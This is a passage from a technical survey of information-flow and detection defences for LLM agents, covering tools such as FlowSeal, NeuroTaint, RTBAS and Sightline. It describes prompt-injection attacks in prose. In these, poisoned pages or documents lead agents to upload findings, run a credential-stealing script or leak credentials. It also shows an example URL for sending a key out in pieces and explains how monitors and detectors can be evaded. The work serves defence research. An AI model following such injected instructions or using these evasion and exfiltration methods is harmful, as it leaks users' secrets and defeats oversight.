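The assistant writes nothing secret in the list of statements, but its choice of which statements to keep reveals the diagnosis. An existing defence instructed the model to check the requester's identity and get Mark's consent before sharing anything. Under earlier attacks, this defence had held leaks to between 1.9% and 3.0% of the private items, but under these three, between 43.8% and 75.6% leaked. The model never started the checks because it didn't identify the interaction as a request for information.

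The team's own defence, FlowSeal, labels each sensitive record with its owner. An interceptor outside the model's conversation examines every call that writes or shares data and, if necessary, has a separate model compare the protected records with the proposed output. Across eight attacks, 0% to 3.3% of items leaked with FlowSeal, and the agent completed 72.4% of harmless tasks, compared with 75.9% for the best alternative. In a test with live Gmail and Notion services, the clean-up attack extracted 34.7% of items from an agent with an earlier defence and none from one with FlowSeal.

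Fixed rules determine when FlowSeal makes the comparison, but a model judges whether the output reveals a protected record, and that judgment comes with no guarantee. Shim and colleagues exclude prompt injection, compromised tools and traffic analysis.

### Labels on files that several agents share

Coding agents often work in the same folder with different permissions. One agent may be allowed to read credentials and another to use the network, with neither allowed to do both. If the first agent writes a password to a shared file and the second uploads the file, both have stayed within their permissions.

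Hegelich, Sarhan and colleagues (2026), in *From Attack Surface to Defense Architecture*, use a ledger to prevent this. It records where the contents of files in the shared folder came from, so a label attached to data in one agent's run still applies when another agent opens the file. Their system, ActiveSecHarness, combines the ledger with operating-system checks on files, processes and network connections.

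The researchers built 12 attacks of five steps each and 12 harmless workflows. A policy that checked whether each step suited the task missed 4 of the attacks. A simple lock, which treated data as either tainted or clean, rejected 10 of the harmless workflows. ActiveSecHarness, with finer labels and the ledger, stopped all the attacks and rejected none of the harmless workflows. The sample is so small, however, that a defence that misses a fifth of such attacks would still stop all 12 about 7% of the time. In a larger test of single actions, the system blocked 93.9% of attacks before the team revised it and 100% afterwards.

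### Who writes the labels

AgentDojo has no labels, so researchers have to add their own. Costa and colleagues marked a field as untrusted if any of the benchmark's attacks appears in it. This rule gives a clear baseline, but operators don't know in advance where attacks will appear.

Jiang and colleagues measured how much it matters who writes the labels. ChainCaps depends on a manifest for each tool, which states where its data comes from and what it can affect. With manifests written by experts, ChainCaps blocked every attack and completed every harmless task. It blocked 90.9% of attacks with manifests written using a checklist, but only 27.3% with naive ones, which also halved the completion rate for harmless tasks. Poor labels did more damage than any weakness the team found in the rule for combining labels.

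GAAP needs similar descriptions of who learns what from each call. The real recipient is not always the service that the agent contacts, as the leaks in deployed assistants showed. An email, for example, reaches both the mail provider and the recipient. Stanley and colleagues say that a description takes minutes to write, and they hope that volunteers will maintain a public library of them. If a service has no description, GAAP assumes that the service may later return everything it has received.

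### How often users have to decide

Labels can't determine whether a release is appropriate, so all these systems leave some decisions to a person or to a policy someone wrote in advance. Prudentia with GPT-5 asked for about one decision in every eleven completed tasks. GAAP asked an average of 1.5 questions per task over 100 tasks, many of which were variations of one another. Without its record of earlier answers, it would have averaged 3.8, and one task would have produced 57 questions instead of 7. The two systems' figures aren't directly comparable because Prudentia asks when untrusted data could influence an action, while GAAP asks the first time a private item is about to go to a new recipient.

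Both evaluations assume that people answer correctly. Kolluri and colleagues count no successful attacks on AgentDojo because they assume a reviewer would refuse every injected call. In Anthropic's trial, however, human testers missed most of the planted dangerous commands. Endorsement makes each answer matter more, since a user who endorses a long email also endorses any instruction hidden in it. Prudentia completed 72.7% of tasks without asking anyone, and this result is more reliable because it doesn't depend on a reviewer.

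### Leaks that the benchmark leaves out

AgentDojo probably contains no attacks that leak a secret through the agent's choice of actions. FIDES guarantees only explicit secrecy, which permits implicit flows, but it stopped every attack that Costa and colleagues considered genuine. If some attacks had encoded a secret in the order of page visits, such a policy could have let them through. AgentDojo's built-in tests also check whether an attack achieved its goal, such as a payment to the attacker, and don't measure what an outsider could infer from a series of harmless calls.

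The newer test sets cover more. ChainCaps's tasks include data that the agent mixes, rewrites and then sends. Some of GAAP's attacks hide private data among tool calls that look intended, and FlowSeal's list of true and false statements tests a real choice channel. None of these papers describes an attack like the one in Lan and colleagues' experiment, where an agent sends a key in four separate requests. Labels should handle this easily, but a direct test would show whether they survive when the model splits and encodes the key.

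### Labels in products

Released agents mostly rely on user approval. Kolluri and colleagues write that OpenAI's Codex, Anthropic's computer-use tool and GitHub Copilot ask for confirmation before consequential actions. Copilot Chat in Microsoft's code editor makes read-only calls without asking and requests approval for the rest. Neither Claude Code's classifier nor Chrome's sets of permitted sites, both described earlier, tracks labels on individual pieces of data.

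Developers can already experiment with finer labels. Microsoft has published code and a tutorial for FIDES, and the code for ChainCaps and GAAP is also public. ChainCaps needs no changes to the agent or its tools and adds only about 0.13 milliseconds to a call, but an operator would still have to write the manifests.

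## Experiments: inferring influence after the model has rewritten the data

Any token (a word or part of a word) in a language model's context may affect what the model writes next, so the cautious tracker leads to label creep. A tracker that searches outputs for copied text can instead miss data that the model has reworded. In an example from *Ghost in the Agent*, a research agent reads a web page containing instructions to include a confidential patient note in its report but to reword it. The report describes the patient's cancer and treatment in new sentences, so a search for the original ones finds nothing.

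Several groups have tried to infer which inputs influenced an output, so that the output has to carry only those inputs' labels. These inferences can be wrong, and the consequences of an error depend on the method.

### NeuroTaint: auditing a finished run

*Ghost in the Agent*, which Yuandao Cai and colleagues published in April 2026, presents NeuroTaint, a program that examines a run after it has finished. It can report a leak but not stop one. It stores the run as a graph in which each node is a tool call and each edge carries a label naming the source of the data. For every call to a sink, NeuroTaint finds the sources with a path to that call and compares each source's text with the call's arguments in four stages:

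1. It looks for a random marker that it attached to the source's text when the agent read it.
2. It measures how much text the source and the argument share, as a fraction of the shorter one. A fraction of 0.15 counts as a match.
3. It converts both texts into lists of numbers that represent their meaning and compares these. A similarity of 0.60 counts as a match, or 0.85 if the source came from memory.
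4. It splits the source into chunks of a few sentences and compares each chunk, so that a short hidden instruction doesn't get lost in a long page.

If no stage finds a match, NeuroTaint runs a counterfactual test. It gives a second model two versions of the agent's history, one unchanged and one with the source's text replaced by something neutral, such as "No relevant information found". The second model judges whether the agent would still have made the call. If not, NeuroTaint reports an implicit flow. In one scenario, a poisoned search result contains an instruction to send all findings to an outside address before running any code, and the agent then uploads its research results there. The upload need not repeat the instruction's text, but the agent would not have made it without the instruction.

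### A forecast that returns three days later

The graph also persists between sessions. In the paper's example, an agent built with the memory library Mem0 reads a confidential forecast on day 1 that puts the revenue of "Project Atlas" at $84.6 million, and saves it to memory. NeuroTaint stores the forecast's label next to the text and saves the graph when the session ends.

On day 4, the user asks for an operations report. The agent retrieves the note, which restores the old label, but the retrieval alone doesn't cause an alarm. When the agent writes in the report that Atlas should earn $84.6 million this quarter, NeuroTaint compares the report with the forecast, finds a match and traces the path back to day 1.

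This result comes mostly from the saved label, and the stored labels in SPA would have had the same effect. The inference adds the ability to clear a report if the agent retrieved the forecast but didn't use it to write the report. Memory was still a weak point for NeuroTaint, which found 7 of the 10 flows in the Mem0 scenarios, its lowest share for any framework.

### TaintBench

The team tested NeuroTaint on its own benchmark, TaintBench, which has 20 scenarios for each of 20 agent frameworks. In 200 of the 400 scenarios, content from a source is supposed to reach or influence a sink, and the other 200 are controls. The agent ran on GPT-4.1 mini. Each scenario ran five times, and the majority verdict counted. The team compared NeuroTaint with a baseline modelled on FIDES, which treats a path from a source to a sink as strong evidence of a flow.

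| Scenarios | Number | NeuroTaint's alarms | Baseline's alarms |
|---|---|---|---|
| Flow: copied text | 60 | 60 | 45 |
| Flow: rewording over several steps | 42 | 35 | 31 |
| Flow: influence on a decision only | 40 | 37 | 17 |
| Flow: across sessions or agents | 30 | 28 | 5 |
| Flow: fragments of a longer source | 15 | 15 | 6 |
| Flow: other | 13 | 12 | 4 |
| Control: source and sink but no flow | 140 | 1 | 94 |
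| Control: clean run | 40 | 0 | 0 |
| Control: same topic as the source | 14 | 14 | 9 |
| Control: facts the model already knew | 6 | 1 | 3 |

NeuroTaint found 187 of the 200 flows and raised 16 false alarms, while the baseline found 108 and raised 106. The F1 score, which combines the share of alarms that are correct with the share of flows found, was 0.928 for NeuroTaint and 0.522 for the baseline.

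NeuroTaint flagged all 14 controls in which the output only shared a topic with the source. Agents often read about a subject and then write about it, so such cases are probably more common in real work than in TaintBench. If these cases had made up half the controls, about 65% of NeuroTaint's alarms would have been correct instead of 92%.

### A baseline no better than a coin toss

The baseline flagged 54% of the flows and 53% of the controls, so it barely distinguished between them. A detector that flagged all 400 scenarios would have scored 0.667, well above the baseline.

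Some of the false alarms arise because FIDES is designed to block forbidden flows when in doubt, and TaintBench counts this caution as an error. Caution can't explain the missed flows, because a cautious tracker should catch any influence on a decision within a run, and the baseline missed 23 of 40 such cases. On four frameworks it raised no alarm in any of the 80 scenarios, which accounts for 40 of its 92 misses. That looks more like a fault in connecting the baseline to those frameworks than a limit of labels, so the comparison is weak evidence about FIDES itself.

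NeuroTaint's score may also be too high. Two of the researchers sensibly settled the correct answer for every scenario before comparing the detectors, but according to the paper, "safe-control policies" used a similarity threshold of 0.95 instead of 0.60. If these policies belong to the control scenarios, NeuroTaint was harder to trigger in the runs where an alarm would have been a false positive. An operator couldn't apply the higher threshold in the same way without knowing in advance which runs are harmless.

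The answers also describe what should happen in a scenario, not what the agent did in a particular run. With Claude Opus 4.6 as the agent, NeuroTaint found only 55% of the flows. Part of this drop is not a detection failure, since a stronger model can refuse the attack, leaving no flow to detect. On two older benchmarks, InjecAgent and ToolEmu, NeuroTaint and the baseline had F1 scores within 0.001 of each other, but those benchmarks test for unsafe actions, not flows.

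The second model predicts the counterfactual without rerunning the agent. Its prediction may be reliable when a page contains an explicit instruction to upload data, since the model can read the cause in the text. It is much harder to predict that an agent would have opened a different public page if a digit in a file had been different.

A reviewing model can reduce false alarms. When Claude Opus 4.6 reviewed NeuroTaint's 203 alarms, it dismissed all 16 false ones and only 8 of the 187 real flows. But the reviewer also received each scenario's identifier and flow type, which may have revealed the answers. An independent test would help, but a suitable one may not exist yet. *From Agent Traces to Trust* (Wang, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) catalogued 26 benchmarks and datasets related to tracing what agents do and found none that evaluates the complete chain of provenance.

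### RTBAS: hiding whatever the inference leaves out

Zhong, Chen and colleagues (2025), in *RTBAS*, make the inference before the agent acts, in four steps:

1. A screener reads the conversation, which is divided into labelled regions, and selects the regions that the next action depends on.
2. RTBAS computes the join of their labels.
3. It blanks out every region that this combined label doesn't cover.
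4. The agent's model sees only what remains and proposes a tool call. RTBAS runs the call if the policy permits the combined label, and otherwise asks the user.

One version of the screener is a second language model. The other uses attention, the weights a model gives to earlier tokens as it writes. A small open model supplies these weights, and a small neural network uses them to predict which regions matter. The network was developed on 40 AgentDojo test cases and was right 81% of the time on test data.

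That would be a poor record if security depended on it, but RTBAS hides any password the screener overlooks, so the model can't send it. Zhong and colleagues therefore argue that the screener's mistakes can make the agent less useful but can't compromise security. This is almost right, except that the screener reads everything, so what it decides to hide can depend on a secret. The paper's simplest scheme has four possible labels, so the choice of label can convey at most 2 bits per step, and a four-digit code would take at least seven steps.

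On AgentDojo with GPT-4o, RTBAS stopped every attack that violated its policy. Without attacks, the share of tasks completed fell by 10% with the language-model screener and 7.4% with the attention screener. The drop was largest on the Slack tasks, where only 22% and 33% were completed, because many of them require the agent to act on text from an untrusted website. These figures assume that the user refuses every doubtful call, so more tasks would be completed if the user approved the legitimate ones.

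The team also wrote 37 tasks in which an agent could accidentally reveal private data while making payments, booking flights or shopping. Asking the user before every call led to unnecessary questions in 11 tasks. The language-model screener reduced this to 3 and the attention screener to 6. Each also failed to ask in 4 tasks where it should have. RTBAS is designed so that such a failure hides data the task needed instead of leaking it. In AgentDojo's banking tasks, both screeners roughly doubled the time and cost.

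### Permissive propagation

In *Permissive Information-Flow Analysis for Large Language Models*, Siddiqui, Gaonkar and colleagues (2025) pass on the labels of only those inputs that influenced the output. They tried one version that puts retrieved documents into the prompt and another that uses a language model that looks up similar stored examples as it writes. In more than 85% of cases tested with an agent, the method improved on asking the model to predict the label itself.

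According to Zhong and colleagues, the method searches for the smallest set of inputs that leads to a similar output, which takes 16 to 64 extra model calls with a typical set of labels. Requiring only a similar output weakens the guarantee. Requests for page 2 and page 7 are nearly identical as text, but an agent spelling out a code can encode its entire message in the page numbers.

### Geometric information flow

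Štorek, Holzer and colleagues (2026), in *GIF*, measure influence inside the model. A language model converts each token into a list of numbers before processing it. Geometric information flow, or GIF, imagines adding a little random noise U to the numbers for one passage, and asks how many bits the next token Y would reveal about that noise. The exact answer is too expensive to compute, so the researchers proved an upper limit:

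I(U; Y) ≤ (τ/2) · tr(M) + o(τ).

Here τ is the variance of the noise, and tr(M) is the total sensitivity of the next-token probabilities to small changes in the passage. The last term is an error that shrinks faster than τ. The proof, which the researchers checked in Lean, assumes that the model behaves smoothly near the actual input.

In the paper's example, an applicant hides an instruction in a CV, and a hiring agent follows it. GIF attributes 82 bits of the recommendation to the hidden instruction, 27 to the employer's criteria and 16 to the remaining text. These bits measure sensitivity to noise, not how much of a secret has leaked, so they could not be counted against a leakage budget.

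The researchers tested GIF on three benchmarks with six open models. For each tool call they ranked the input tokens by influence and counted how many of the top 50 were injected or private. They then checked how often a random run with a violation had a higher count than a random run without one, where guessing would give 50%:

| Method | AgentDojo (injection) | MSB (injection) | AgentDAM (privacy) |
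|---|---|---|---|
| GIF | 91% | 92% | 75% |
| RTBAS's attention method | 84% | 76% | 57% |

GIF was clearly weaker on privacy than on injection. The test also relied on the benchmarks' labels for which tokens were private or malicious. In practical use, GIF would select the most influential passages and another model would judge whether to allow the call. Judges given only these passages did about as well as judges given the whole run, or better. With a single passage per call, they used 63% to 73% fewer tokens on the two injection benchmarks. Measuring influence doesn't require access to the agent's own model. Replacing a 120-billion-parameter model with a 0.6-billion-parameter one changed the F1 score by less than a point.

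GIF's guarantee covers only how small changes to a passage affect the next token. Replacing one password with another is not a small change, so the guarantee doesn't cover the comparison that matters for a secret.

### Influence that leaves almost no trace

Xu, Li and colleagues (2026), in *Sightline*, proved that this gap can hide a complete dependence. Their argument fits the agent that spells out a code through page visits. Let u be 1 if the next digit is 7 and −1 if it is 2, and suppose the model opens page 7 instead of page 2 with probability

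1 / (1 + e^(−20u)).

If the digit is 7, the model is practically certain to open page 7. Changing u slightly makes almost no difference, so GIF measures a sensitivity of only about 0.0000008. But changing the digit to 2 reverses the choice. A confident decision can therefore reveal the digit completely even when GIF gives a value near zero.

They also prove that low attention to an input doesn't rule out its influence either. Their third result is that tests that remove one input at a time can miss influence. If a password appears in two files, removing either copy leaves the output unchanged, so the test reports that neither file had an influence. NeuroTaint's counterfactual question has the same weakness because it replaces only one source at a time.

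Since no such signal can prove that an input had no influence, Xu and colleagues accepted a known error rate. Their tool, Sightline, records how much each part of the model attends to an input, and is trained on labelled examples to recognise patterns that indicate the model used that input. It sets its threshold so that, on average, it misses at most a chosen share of real flows. The team tested it with four open models on prompts from 2,103 groups of related open-source projects. Set to a 1% miss rate, Sightline removed 44% to 66% of the unnecessary labels and missed about 1% of real flows. It took at most a fifth of a second per call. In a test with an agent, it removed about half of the unnecessary labels.

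The gain in usefulness may be modest, because only 12% to 14% of the inputs in the project prompts had no effect on the output. Removing the labels from about half of those inputs eliminates roughly 5% to 9% of all labels. Better inference can't remove the labels of inputs that did influence the output. An agent's long history probably contains more irrelevant material than a single prompt, so the gain may be larger for agents.

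The 1% is also an average over prompts like those used to set the threshold, so an attacker can look for unusual prompts on which Sightline fails. Misses add up when a label has to survive several rewritings. If each rewriting loses the label 1% of the time, independently of the others, ten successive rewritings lose it about 10% of the time.

### A key in four pieces

None of these papers tests the case in the experiment by Lan and colleagues, where an agent sends a secret in pieces through several calls. TaintBench has a group of "multi-fragment" scenarios, but the matching stage for them splits the source into chunks and doesn't put the arguments of several calls back together.

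NeuroTaint's text matching would probably miss a small piece of a key. The address `https://example.com/?d=SECR` has 27 characters, and only four come from the key. If the file with the key is longer than the address and only unbroken stretches count as shared text, the shared fraction is 4/27, or 0.148, just under the threshold of 0.15. Four letters also have too little meaning for the other comparisons to work. NeuroTaint checks each call separately, so it wouldn't combine four weak matches into a strong one.

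The counterfactual question might also expose the leak, if the second model infers that the agent couldn't have written "SECR" without reading the key, or that it would have sent nothing without the malicious page. Leaks through visits to public pages are harder to catch this way if the user asked the agent to browse the site, because the second model would have to detect that the order of the visits spells the code.

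GIF and Sightline measure influence without matching text, so they can in principle detect a short piece of data. The closest test used whole values rather than pieces. Xu and colleagues planted names, words, numbers and web addresses in prompts, and in 476 cases the value appeared unchanged in the output. Sightline flagged all 476. RTBAS's attention network, which the team retrained and ran without hiding any data, found between 42% and 77% of them, depending on the model.

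With the hiding step, RTBAS should be the best at handling a key sent in pieces, although this too is untested. If the screener selects the key, every request the model writes carries the key's label, however short the piece of the key in it. If the screener doesn't select the key, RTBAS hides it, so the model can't split it. The same reasoning applies to page visits that depend on a code, except for the few bits that the screener's choices can reveal. RTBAS also labels the agent's replies and the results of its calls, so a piece that the agent repeats there stays restricted in later steps.

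## Experiments: detectors that read the whole sequence

Most of the systems in the last two sections depend on someone correctly labeling which data is secret or untrusted. A learned detector doesn't need these labels, but it isn't guaranteed to catch any particular kind of leak. Developers train it on records of past sessions, some attacked and some normal. It then scores each new session by how closely that session resembles the attacked ones, and raises an alarm if the score is above a chosen threshold.

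### What a detector can learn from tool calls

*Content-Aware Attack Detection in LLM Agent Tool-Call Traffic* (Zavrak, 2026) tested how much of a session such a detector needs as input. The main dataset, RAS-Eval, had 605 normal sessions and 3,797 in which an attacker had changed what the agent sent to its tools, what the tools returned, or both. Some detectors received only metadata: the name of each tool, a hash of its arguments and the length of its result. Others received the text of the arguments and results, converted into lists of numbers that represent its meaning.

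The comparison uses AUROC, the chance that a random attacked session scores higher than a random normal one. Guessing gives 50%.

| Detector | Input | AUROC |
|---|---|---|
| Neural network that uses links between calls | Metadata | 64.0% |
| The same network | Text | 91.7% |
| Neural network without links | Text | 89.6% |
| Decision trees (XGBoost) | Text | 97.5% |

The best detector in the table ignores the order of the calls. Its decision trees receive only the average and maximum of each number over all calls in a session, so shuffling the calls doesn't change the score. An agent that spells out 7294 by visiting pages 7, 2, 9 and 4 would get the same score as one that visits them in ascending order. The high AUROC suggests that attacks in this dataset leave traces in the text of individual calls, but it isn't evidence that the detector could find a leak that depends on order.

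The links in the first network are a rough form of taint tracking. The software links two calls if one call's arguments contain the first 50 characters of the other's result, or one of that result's first five words, provided the word is longer than four characters. It skips results longer than 1,000 characters. A password in the middle of a configuration file would usually create no link, and neither would a four-character piece of a key.

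Zavrak also found that a careless test can make metadata look useful. When sessions from the same task appeared in both the training and the test data, a metadata detector reached 89.8%, because it could learn which tools belong to which task. When the tasks were kept separate, it fell to 64.0%. The text detectors may have partly relied on a model's style, since all the attacked sessions came from one language model and the normal ones from eight. Detection was worst when the attacker changed only the arguments, such as a file path. In one test, the linked network caught 37% of these sessions.

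### AgentDrift: an attack marked step by step

*AgentDrift* (Pinjari and Saint-Germain, 2026) presents a dataset of 12,536 synthetic sessions for training detectors that find the point where an attack begins. The dataset labels each of the sessions' 71,024 steps as ordinary, as the entry point of an injected instruction, as hijacked, or as an injection that the agent resisted. It also includes 1,500 sessions with legitimate content that looks suspicious, such as a genuine request to send a report to the company's own auditors.

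In one attacked session, a user asks a banking agent to apply for a loan and check the fees. The agent checks the user's credit score and balance as usual. The fee lookup then returns a fake policy that requires sending sensitive information to an outside "security audit" address, and the agent adds that address to the user's payees.

The attacks follow three patterns. A simple detector, which used six features such as the number of steps, outside recipients and suspicious words, caught very different shares of them:

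| Pattern | What the agent does after the injection | Caught |
|---|---|---|
| Full hijack | Works only for the attacker | 88.0% |
| Partial hijack | Follows the attacker for one or two steps, then returns to the task | 8.2% |
| Delayed execution | Continues the task and adds one harmful step later | 23.1% |

The detector also flagged 10.5% of normal sessions, so it was less likely to flag a partial hijack than a normal session. Pinjari and Saint-Germain concluded that the harder patterns require a model of the whole sequence.

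Later results on the same data contradict this. In *What Standard Evaluations Hide About Detectors of Hijacked LLM Agents*, Abbasi, Núñez and Shahraki (2026) built a detector that only counts words and pairs of neighbouring words, and it reached an AUROC of 99.9%. It had learned patterns in the text of the model that generated the dataset. For example, the string "2026" appears in 74% of the normal training sessions but only 5% of the attacked ones. Pinjari and Saint-Germain had themselves reported a similar flaw, in which guessing from the fictional user's identity alone was right 86.1% of the time because many of the users appear in only one type of session.

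They also found that a language model was a poor judge of suspicious but harmless sessions. When they asked the model that had generated the dataset to check it, the model rejected 1,494 of the 1,500 legitimate sessions, mostly because they looked like attacks.

### Ten thousand alarms for 95 attacks

About 44% of AgentDrift's sessions contain a successful attack. In the eleven published evaluations that Abbasi and colleagues reviewed, the share of attacks or anomalies ranged from 16% to 86%. Real attacks are presumably much rarer, so an alarm in real use would be less likely to indicate an attack than an alarm in these tests.

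Let π be the share of sessions with an attack, d the share of attacks that the detector catches, and f the share of normal sessions that it flags by mistake. The share of alarms that are correct is

πd / (πd + (1 − π)f).

Suppose that one session in 10,000 is attacked and that a detector catches 95% of attacks with a false-alarm rate of 1%. In a million sessions, it would catch 95 of the 100 attacks and falsely flag 9,999 of the other 999,900 sessions. Less than 1% of its roughly 10,100 alarms would be correct. If an analyst spent five minutes on each alarm, reviewing them all would take more than 800 hours.

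For half of the alarms to be correct, the false-alarm rate would have to fall to about one in 10,500. The detectors in these experiments have far higher rates. One that combined tool names with simple features of the session had an AUROC of 87.9%, caught 77.1% of attacks and flagged 19.2% of normal sessions. Abbasi and colleagues calculate that if 2% of sessions were attacked, it would raise 12 false alarms for every correct one. If one session in 10,000 were attacked, there would be about 2,500 false alarms for every correct one.

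The share of correct alarms also depends on what the harmless sessions contain. At a 2% attack rate, 11.7% of this detector's alarms would be correct if all the harmless sessions were ordinary, and 3.9% if they all contained suspicious-looking content. An agent that often handles invoices and security notices would therefore cause more false alarms than these averages suggest.

Very low false-alarm rates are also hard to measure. The word-counting detector flagged none of the 825 harmless sessions in its test, but its actual false-alarm rate could be as high as 0.4%. At that rate, if one session in 10,000 were an attack, about 98% of the detector's alarms would be false. Showing with 95% confidence that the rate is below one in 10,000 would take about 30,000 harmless sessions with no alarms.

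A second check can help if its mistakes are independent of the first detector's. If it also has the same error rates as the detector in the million-session example, it leaves about 90 correct alarms and 100 false ones. But two monitors that read the same trace will probably misread some of the same sessions.

### Unfamiliar tools and attacks

An agent's tools change over time, so Abbasi and colleagues tested detectors on tools they had never seen. One was a small neural network that reads the tool names in order. With familiar tools, its AUROC was 93.6% and it flagged 4.5% of harmless sessions. When the researchers hid every tool name, the AUROC fell to 67.4% and the false-alarm rate rose to 73.7%. Hiding some names during training kept the false-alarm rate at 7% or below, but the AUROC still fell to 79.4%.

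Much of what this network had learned about unfamiliar tools came from the length of their results, which an attacker can change. Adding 1,200 characters to the injected text reduced the share of attacks that the network caught from 68.2% to zero. (The team did not test whether agents would still follow the longer injections.)

Detectors did even worse when tested on a different benchmark. The team trained five detectors on AgentDrift and tested them on recorded AgentDojo sessions, where their AUROC was between 47% and 52%, no better than guessing. Detectors of the same kinds trained on AgentDojo reached 74% to 99.6%, but here too the best score was partly an artefact. A rule that searched for five fixed phrases used in AgentDojo's attacks reached 99.8% without training.

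One monitor, Meta's AlignmentCheck, worked on both benchmarks. It gives a language model the user's request and the agent's actions so far, and has it judge whether the latest action serves a goal that the user didn't set. The prompt includes the arguments of each call but not the results, so the model never receives the injected text directly. Without training on either benchmark, AlignmentCheck had an AUROC of about 93% on AgentDojo with both Llama 3.3 and Claude Sonnet 5.5.

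Its false-alarm rate was less consistent. With Claude, it caught 88.3% of the hijacked AgentDojo sessions and flagged 3.8% of the normal ones, but it flagged 31.3% of AgentDrift's harmless sessions. If one session in 10,000 were an attack, even the 3.8% rate would produce about 430 false alarms for every attack caught.

AlignmentCheck is also poorly suited to detecting accidental leaks, such as the credentials in the first section's summary of an environment file, because every action in that example serves the user's request.

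### An attack assembled over five turns

*ASEval* (Ma, Du et al., 2026) tested whether agents notice an attack that builds up during a conversation. The researchers ran 1,512 attack tests against OpenClaw, an open-source agent with access to the user's files and command line, using eleven language models in turn. Each test ran three times. Attacks spread over several turns succeeded at least once in 51.3% of cases, compared with 40.9% for attacks in a single user message and 13.6% for attacks in a single tool result. The three groups contain different attacks, so the timing may not explain the whole difference.

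In one five-turn test, the user's messages introduced parts of a script as routine maintenance code. The complete script collected credentials and sent them to an outside server. Ten of the eleven models ran it on the fifth turn, while Claude Sonnet 4.5 recognized what it did and refused. When the script ran, the reply to the user mentioned only that diagnostics had been submitted, so a check on the agent's answers would have missed the theft.

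This is an explicit flow, and a label on the credentials could have stopped it if tracking had continued inside the script. ChainCaps lost track of data in scripts that an agent wrote to run later. Flume labels whole processes, so its labels would still have applied and blocked the script's network access.

Ma and colleagues also tried two existing guard models, which judged the conversation so far at each turn. Llama Guard 3 detected between 2.7% and 5.6% of harmful runs, depending on the agent's model and the type of attack. Qwen3Guard detected between 3.3% and 17.8%. Where it detected only 3.3%, it also flagged 2.7% of harmless conversations, so its alarms barely distinguished harmful runs from harmless ones. Access to the conversation's history was evidently not enough for these models to recognize most of the attacks.

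The judge that scored the experiment, Claude Opus 4.5, did much better. It read the complete trace along with rules describing the harm that each test was meant to cause. In a sample of 200 runs, it found 96% of those that a person had marked as harmful and raised five false alarms among the roughly 150 others. But a deployed monitor wouldn't know which attack to look for, and even at the same false alarm rate, it would raise about 33,000 false alarms in a million normal sessions.

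Another test shows why a detector may need information from earlier sessions. A planted document told the agent to include full connection details and configuration files in future documentation, and the user asked the agent to remember the document's conventions. The agent leaked nothing when the user next asked for a summary, but when the user then asked for a guide for a new colleague, all eleven models put credentials in it. If that last request had come in a later session, a detector reading only that session would have had no record of the planted document, just an ordinary request and an agent carrying it out. A stored integrity label would have preserved the link to the document.

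### Checking the split-key experiment

Lan and colleagues ran the closest test so far of a secret sent in fragments, in which a malicious page asked for a key in four separate requests. They define a completion rate, the share of runs in which all four pieces arrive, but report no figures for it, so it is unclear how often the attacker could have reconstructed the key.

The fall in recognizable data in the first request is also ambiguous. The paper counts any fragment of the key as sensitive, so a correctly split key should still count. In many runs the agent may have sent the wrong text, which would mean the attack failed, not that it was hard to detect.

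The example requests also contain a piece number and the total number of pieces, so a simple rule that compared consecutive requests could have detected them. Lan and colleagues recommend such a comparison but did not test it. In their tests with an unsplit key, a list of approved domains blocked every attempt. Because the list doesn't depend on what a request contains, it should work equally well against fragments, provided that the attacker can't receive data through an approved domain.

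One of the paper's results for content filters is doubtful. The agent never tried to send the key when a filter for random-looking text was on. That filter flags long values with more than 4 bits of entropy per character, but the paper's example key, SECRET_API_KEY_12345, has about 3.85. If the runs used that key, the filter couldn't have blocked it, and something else must have stopped the agent.

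### Searching for planted secrets

*Understanding and Evaluating Claw-like Agent Security Through a Computer-Systems Lens* scores its 146 tasks on data crossing boundaries without a learned detector. The benchmark plants credentials that contain unique strings, called canaries, and searches for them in nine output channels, including the agent's replies, outgoing messages, memory and logs. A random string almost never appears in the wrong place by accident, so canaries produce few false alarms even when attacks are rare. An operator could use the same method by planting credentials that no legitimate task needs.

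Depending on the agent software and the model, attacks succeeded in 4.8% to 67.8% of the tasks. The lowest rate was for Claude Opus 4.6 on the NemoClaw agent, but many of the tasks that didn't count as successful attacks in that test must also have leaked some credentials. The average security score was 0.67, where 1 means that no credentials leaked and more serious credentials count for more. If only 4.8% of tasks had leaked anything, the average would have been at least 0.95.

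Extra protection in the agent software also had mixed effects. In SeClaw, a hardened variant of OpenClaw, the success rate with GPT-5.4 fell from 67.8% to 14.4%, but with Opus 4.6 it rose from 8.2% to 17.1%. One reason for such increases is that SeClaw sends notifications through a tool with a required text field, and some models that had left credentials out of ordinary messages put them in that field.

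The canary search looks only for the planted string itself, so it could miss a key that the agent encoded or split across several messages, and it would certainly miss one spelled out through page visits. The measured rates are therefore a lower limit on what leaked.

### Leaks between cooperating agents

When several agents share a task, information can leak even if each agent behaves normally. For example, a user might tell a scheduling agent the medical reason for an absence, and the scheduling agent might forward it without the user's approval to a travel-booking agent that only needs the dates.

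Ogundoyin and Ikram (2026), in *When Agents Talk, Secrets Travel*, ran 485 scenarios without an attacker, varying the number of agents and the rules for which agents could talk to each other. Protected information reached agents outside the original pair in up to 52.2% of cases, depending on the arrangement. With only the original pair, this rate was zero by definition. Total leakage stayed between 60.6% and 62.8% across arrangements, so an operator who measured only the total would have missed where the information went.

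Their defence, RECONS, searches messages for protected information, checks whether the recipient is allowed to have it, and disguises it if not. RECONS lowered the rate of unauthorized disclosure from 96.7% to 29.25% and preserved 94.1% of the permitted disclosures. Removing every protected item that the detector found lowered the rate to 28.3%, but preserved only 20.5% of the permitted disclosures.

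In 95.5% of the remaining leaks, the detector failed to recognize the protected information, which a better rule about recipients can't fix. If a label were attached to the information at its source and stayed attached, the detector would not have to recognize the information again after an agent reworded it. The operator would still need to know who receives each message, and only two of the seven channels that Ogundoyin and Ikram monitored identify a recipient.

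### Long runs and running totals

These experiments use short sessions. AgentDrift's sessions have 3 to 11 steps, and conversations in ASEval average about 3.5 turns. The network that reads tool names keeps only the last 16 calls. If an agent reads a key and sends it 20 calls later, the network's input no longer includes the read when it evaluates the session. An agent that works for hours could easily exceed that limit even if no attacker planned it.

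A stored label or a counter doesn't have this problem, since neither has to keep the whole history. The running-total guard in the calendar test by Pandey and colleagues also raised no false alarms in 120 harmless runs. Those runs alone show only that the false-alarm rate is probably below 2.5%. A better reason to expect few false alarms is that the guard calculates whether the agent has exceeded a fixed limit, whereas a detector that infers an attack from its resemblance to past ones can be wrong. But the guard needs a way to measure how much each action discloses, which is much easier for calendar entries than for free text.

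## Experiments: comparing two runs of the same agent

A detector that reads only one session can't determine whether the agent would have acted differently with another secret, so several methods add a second run. Some compare the two runs and report any difference. Secure multi-execution instead controls which run may send anything to an outsider, so it doesn't need to detect the leak.

### Two copies of one program

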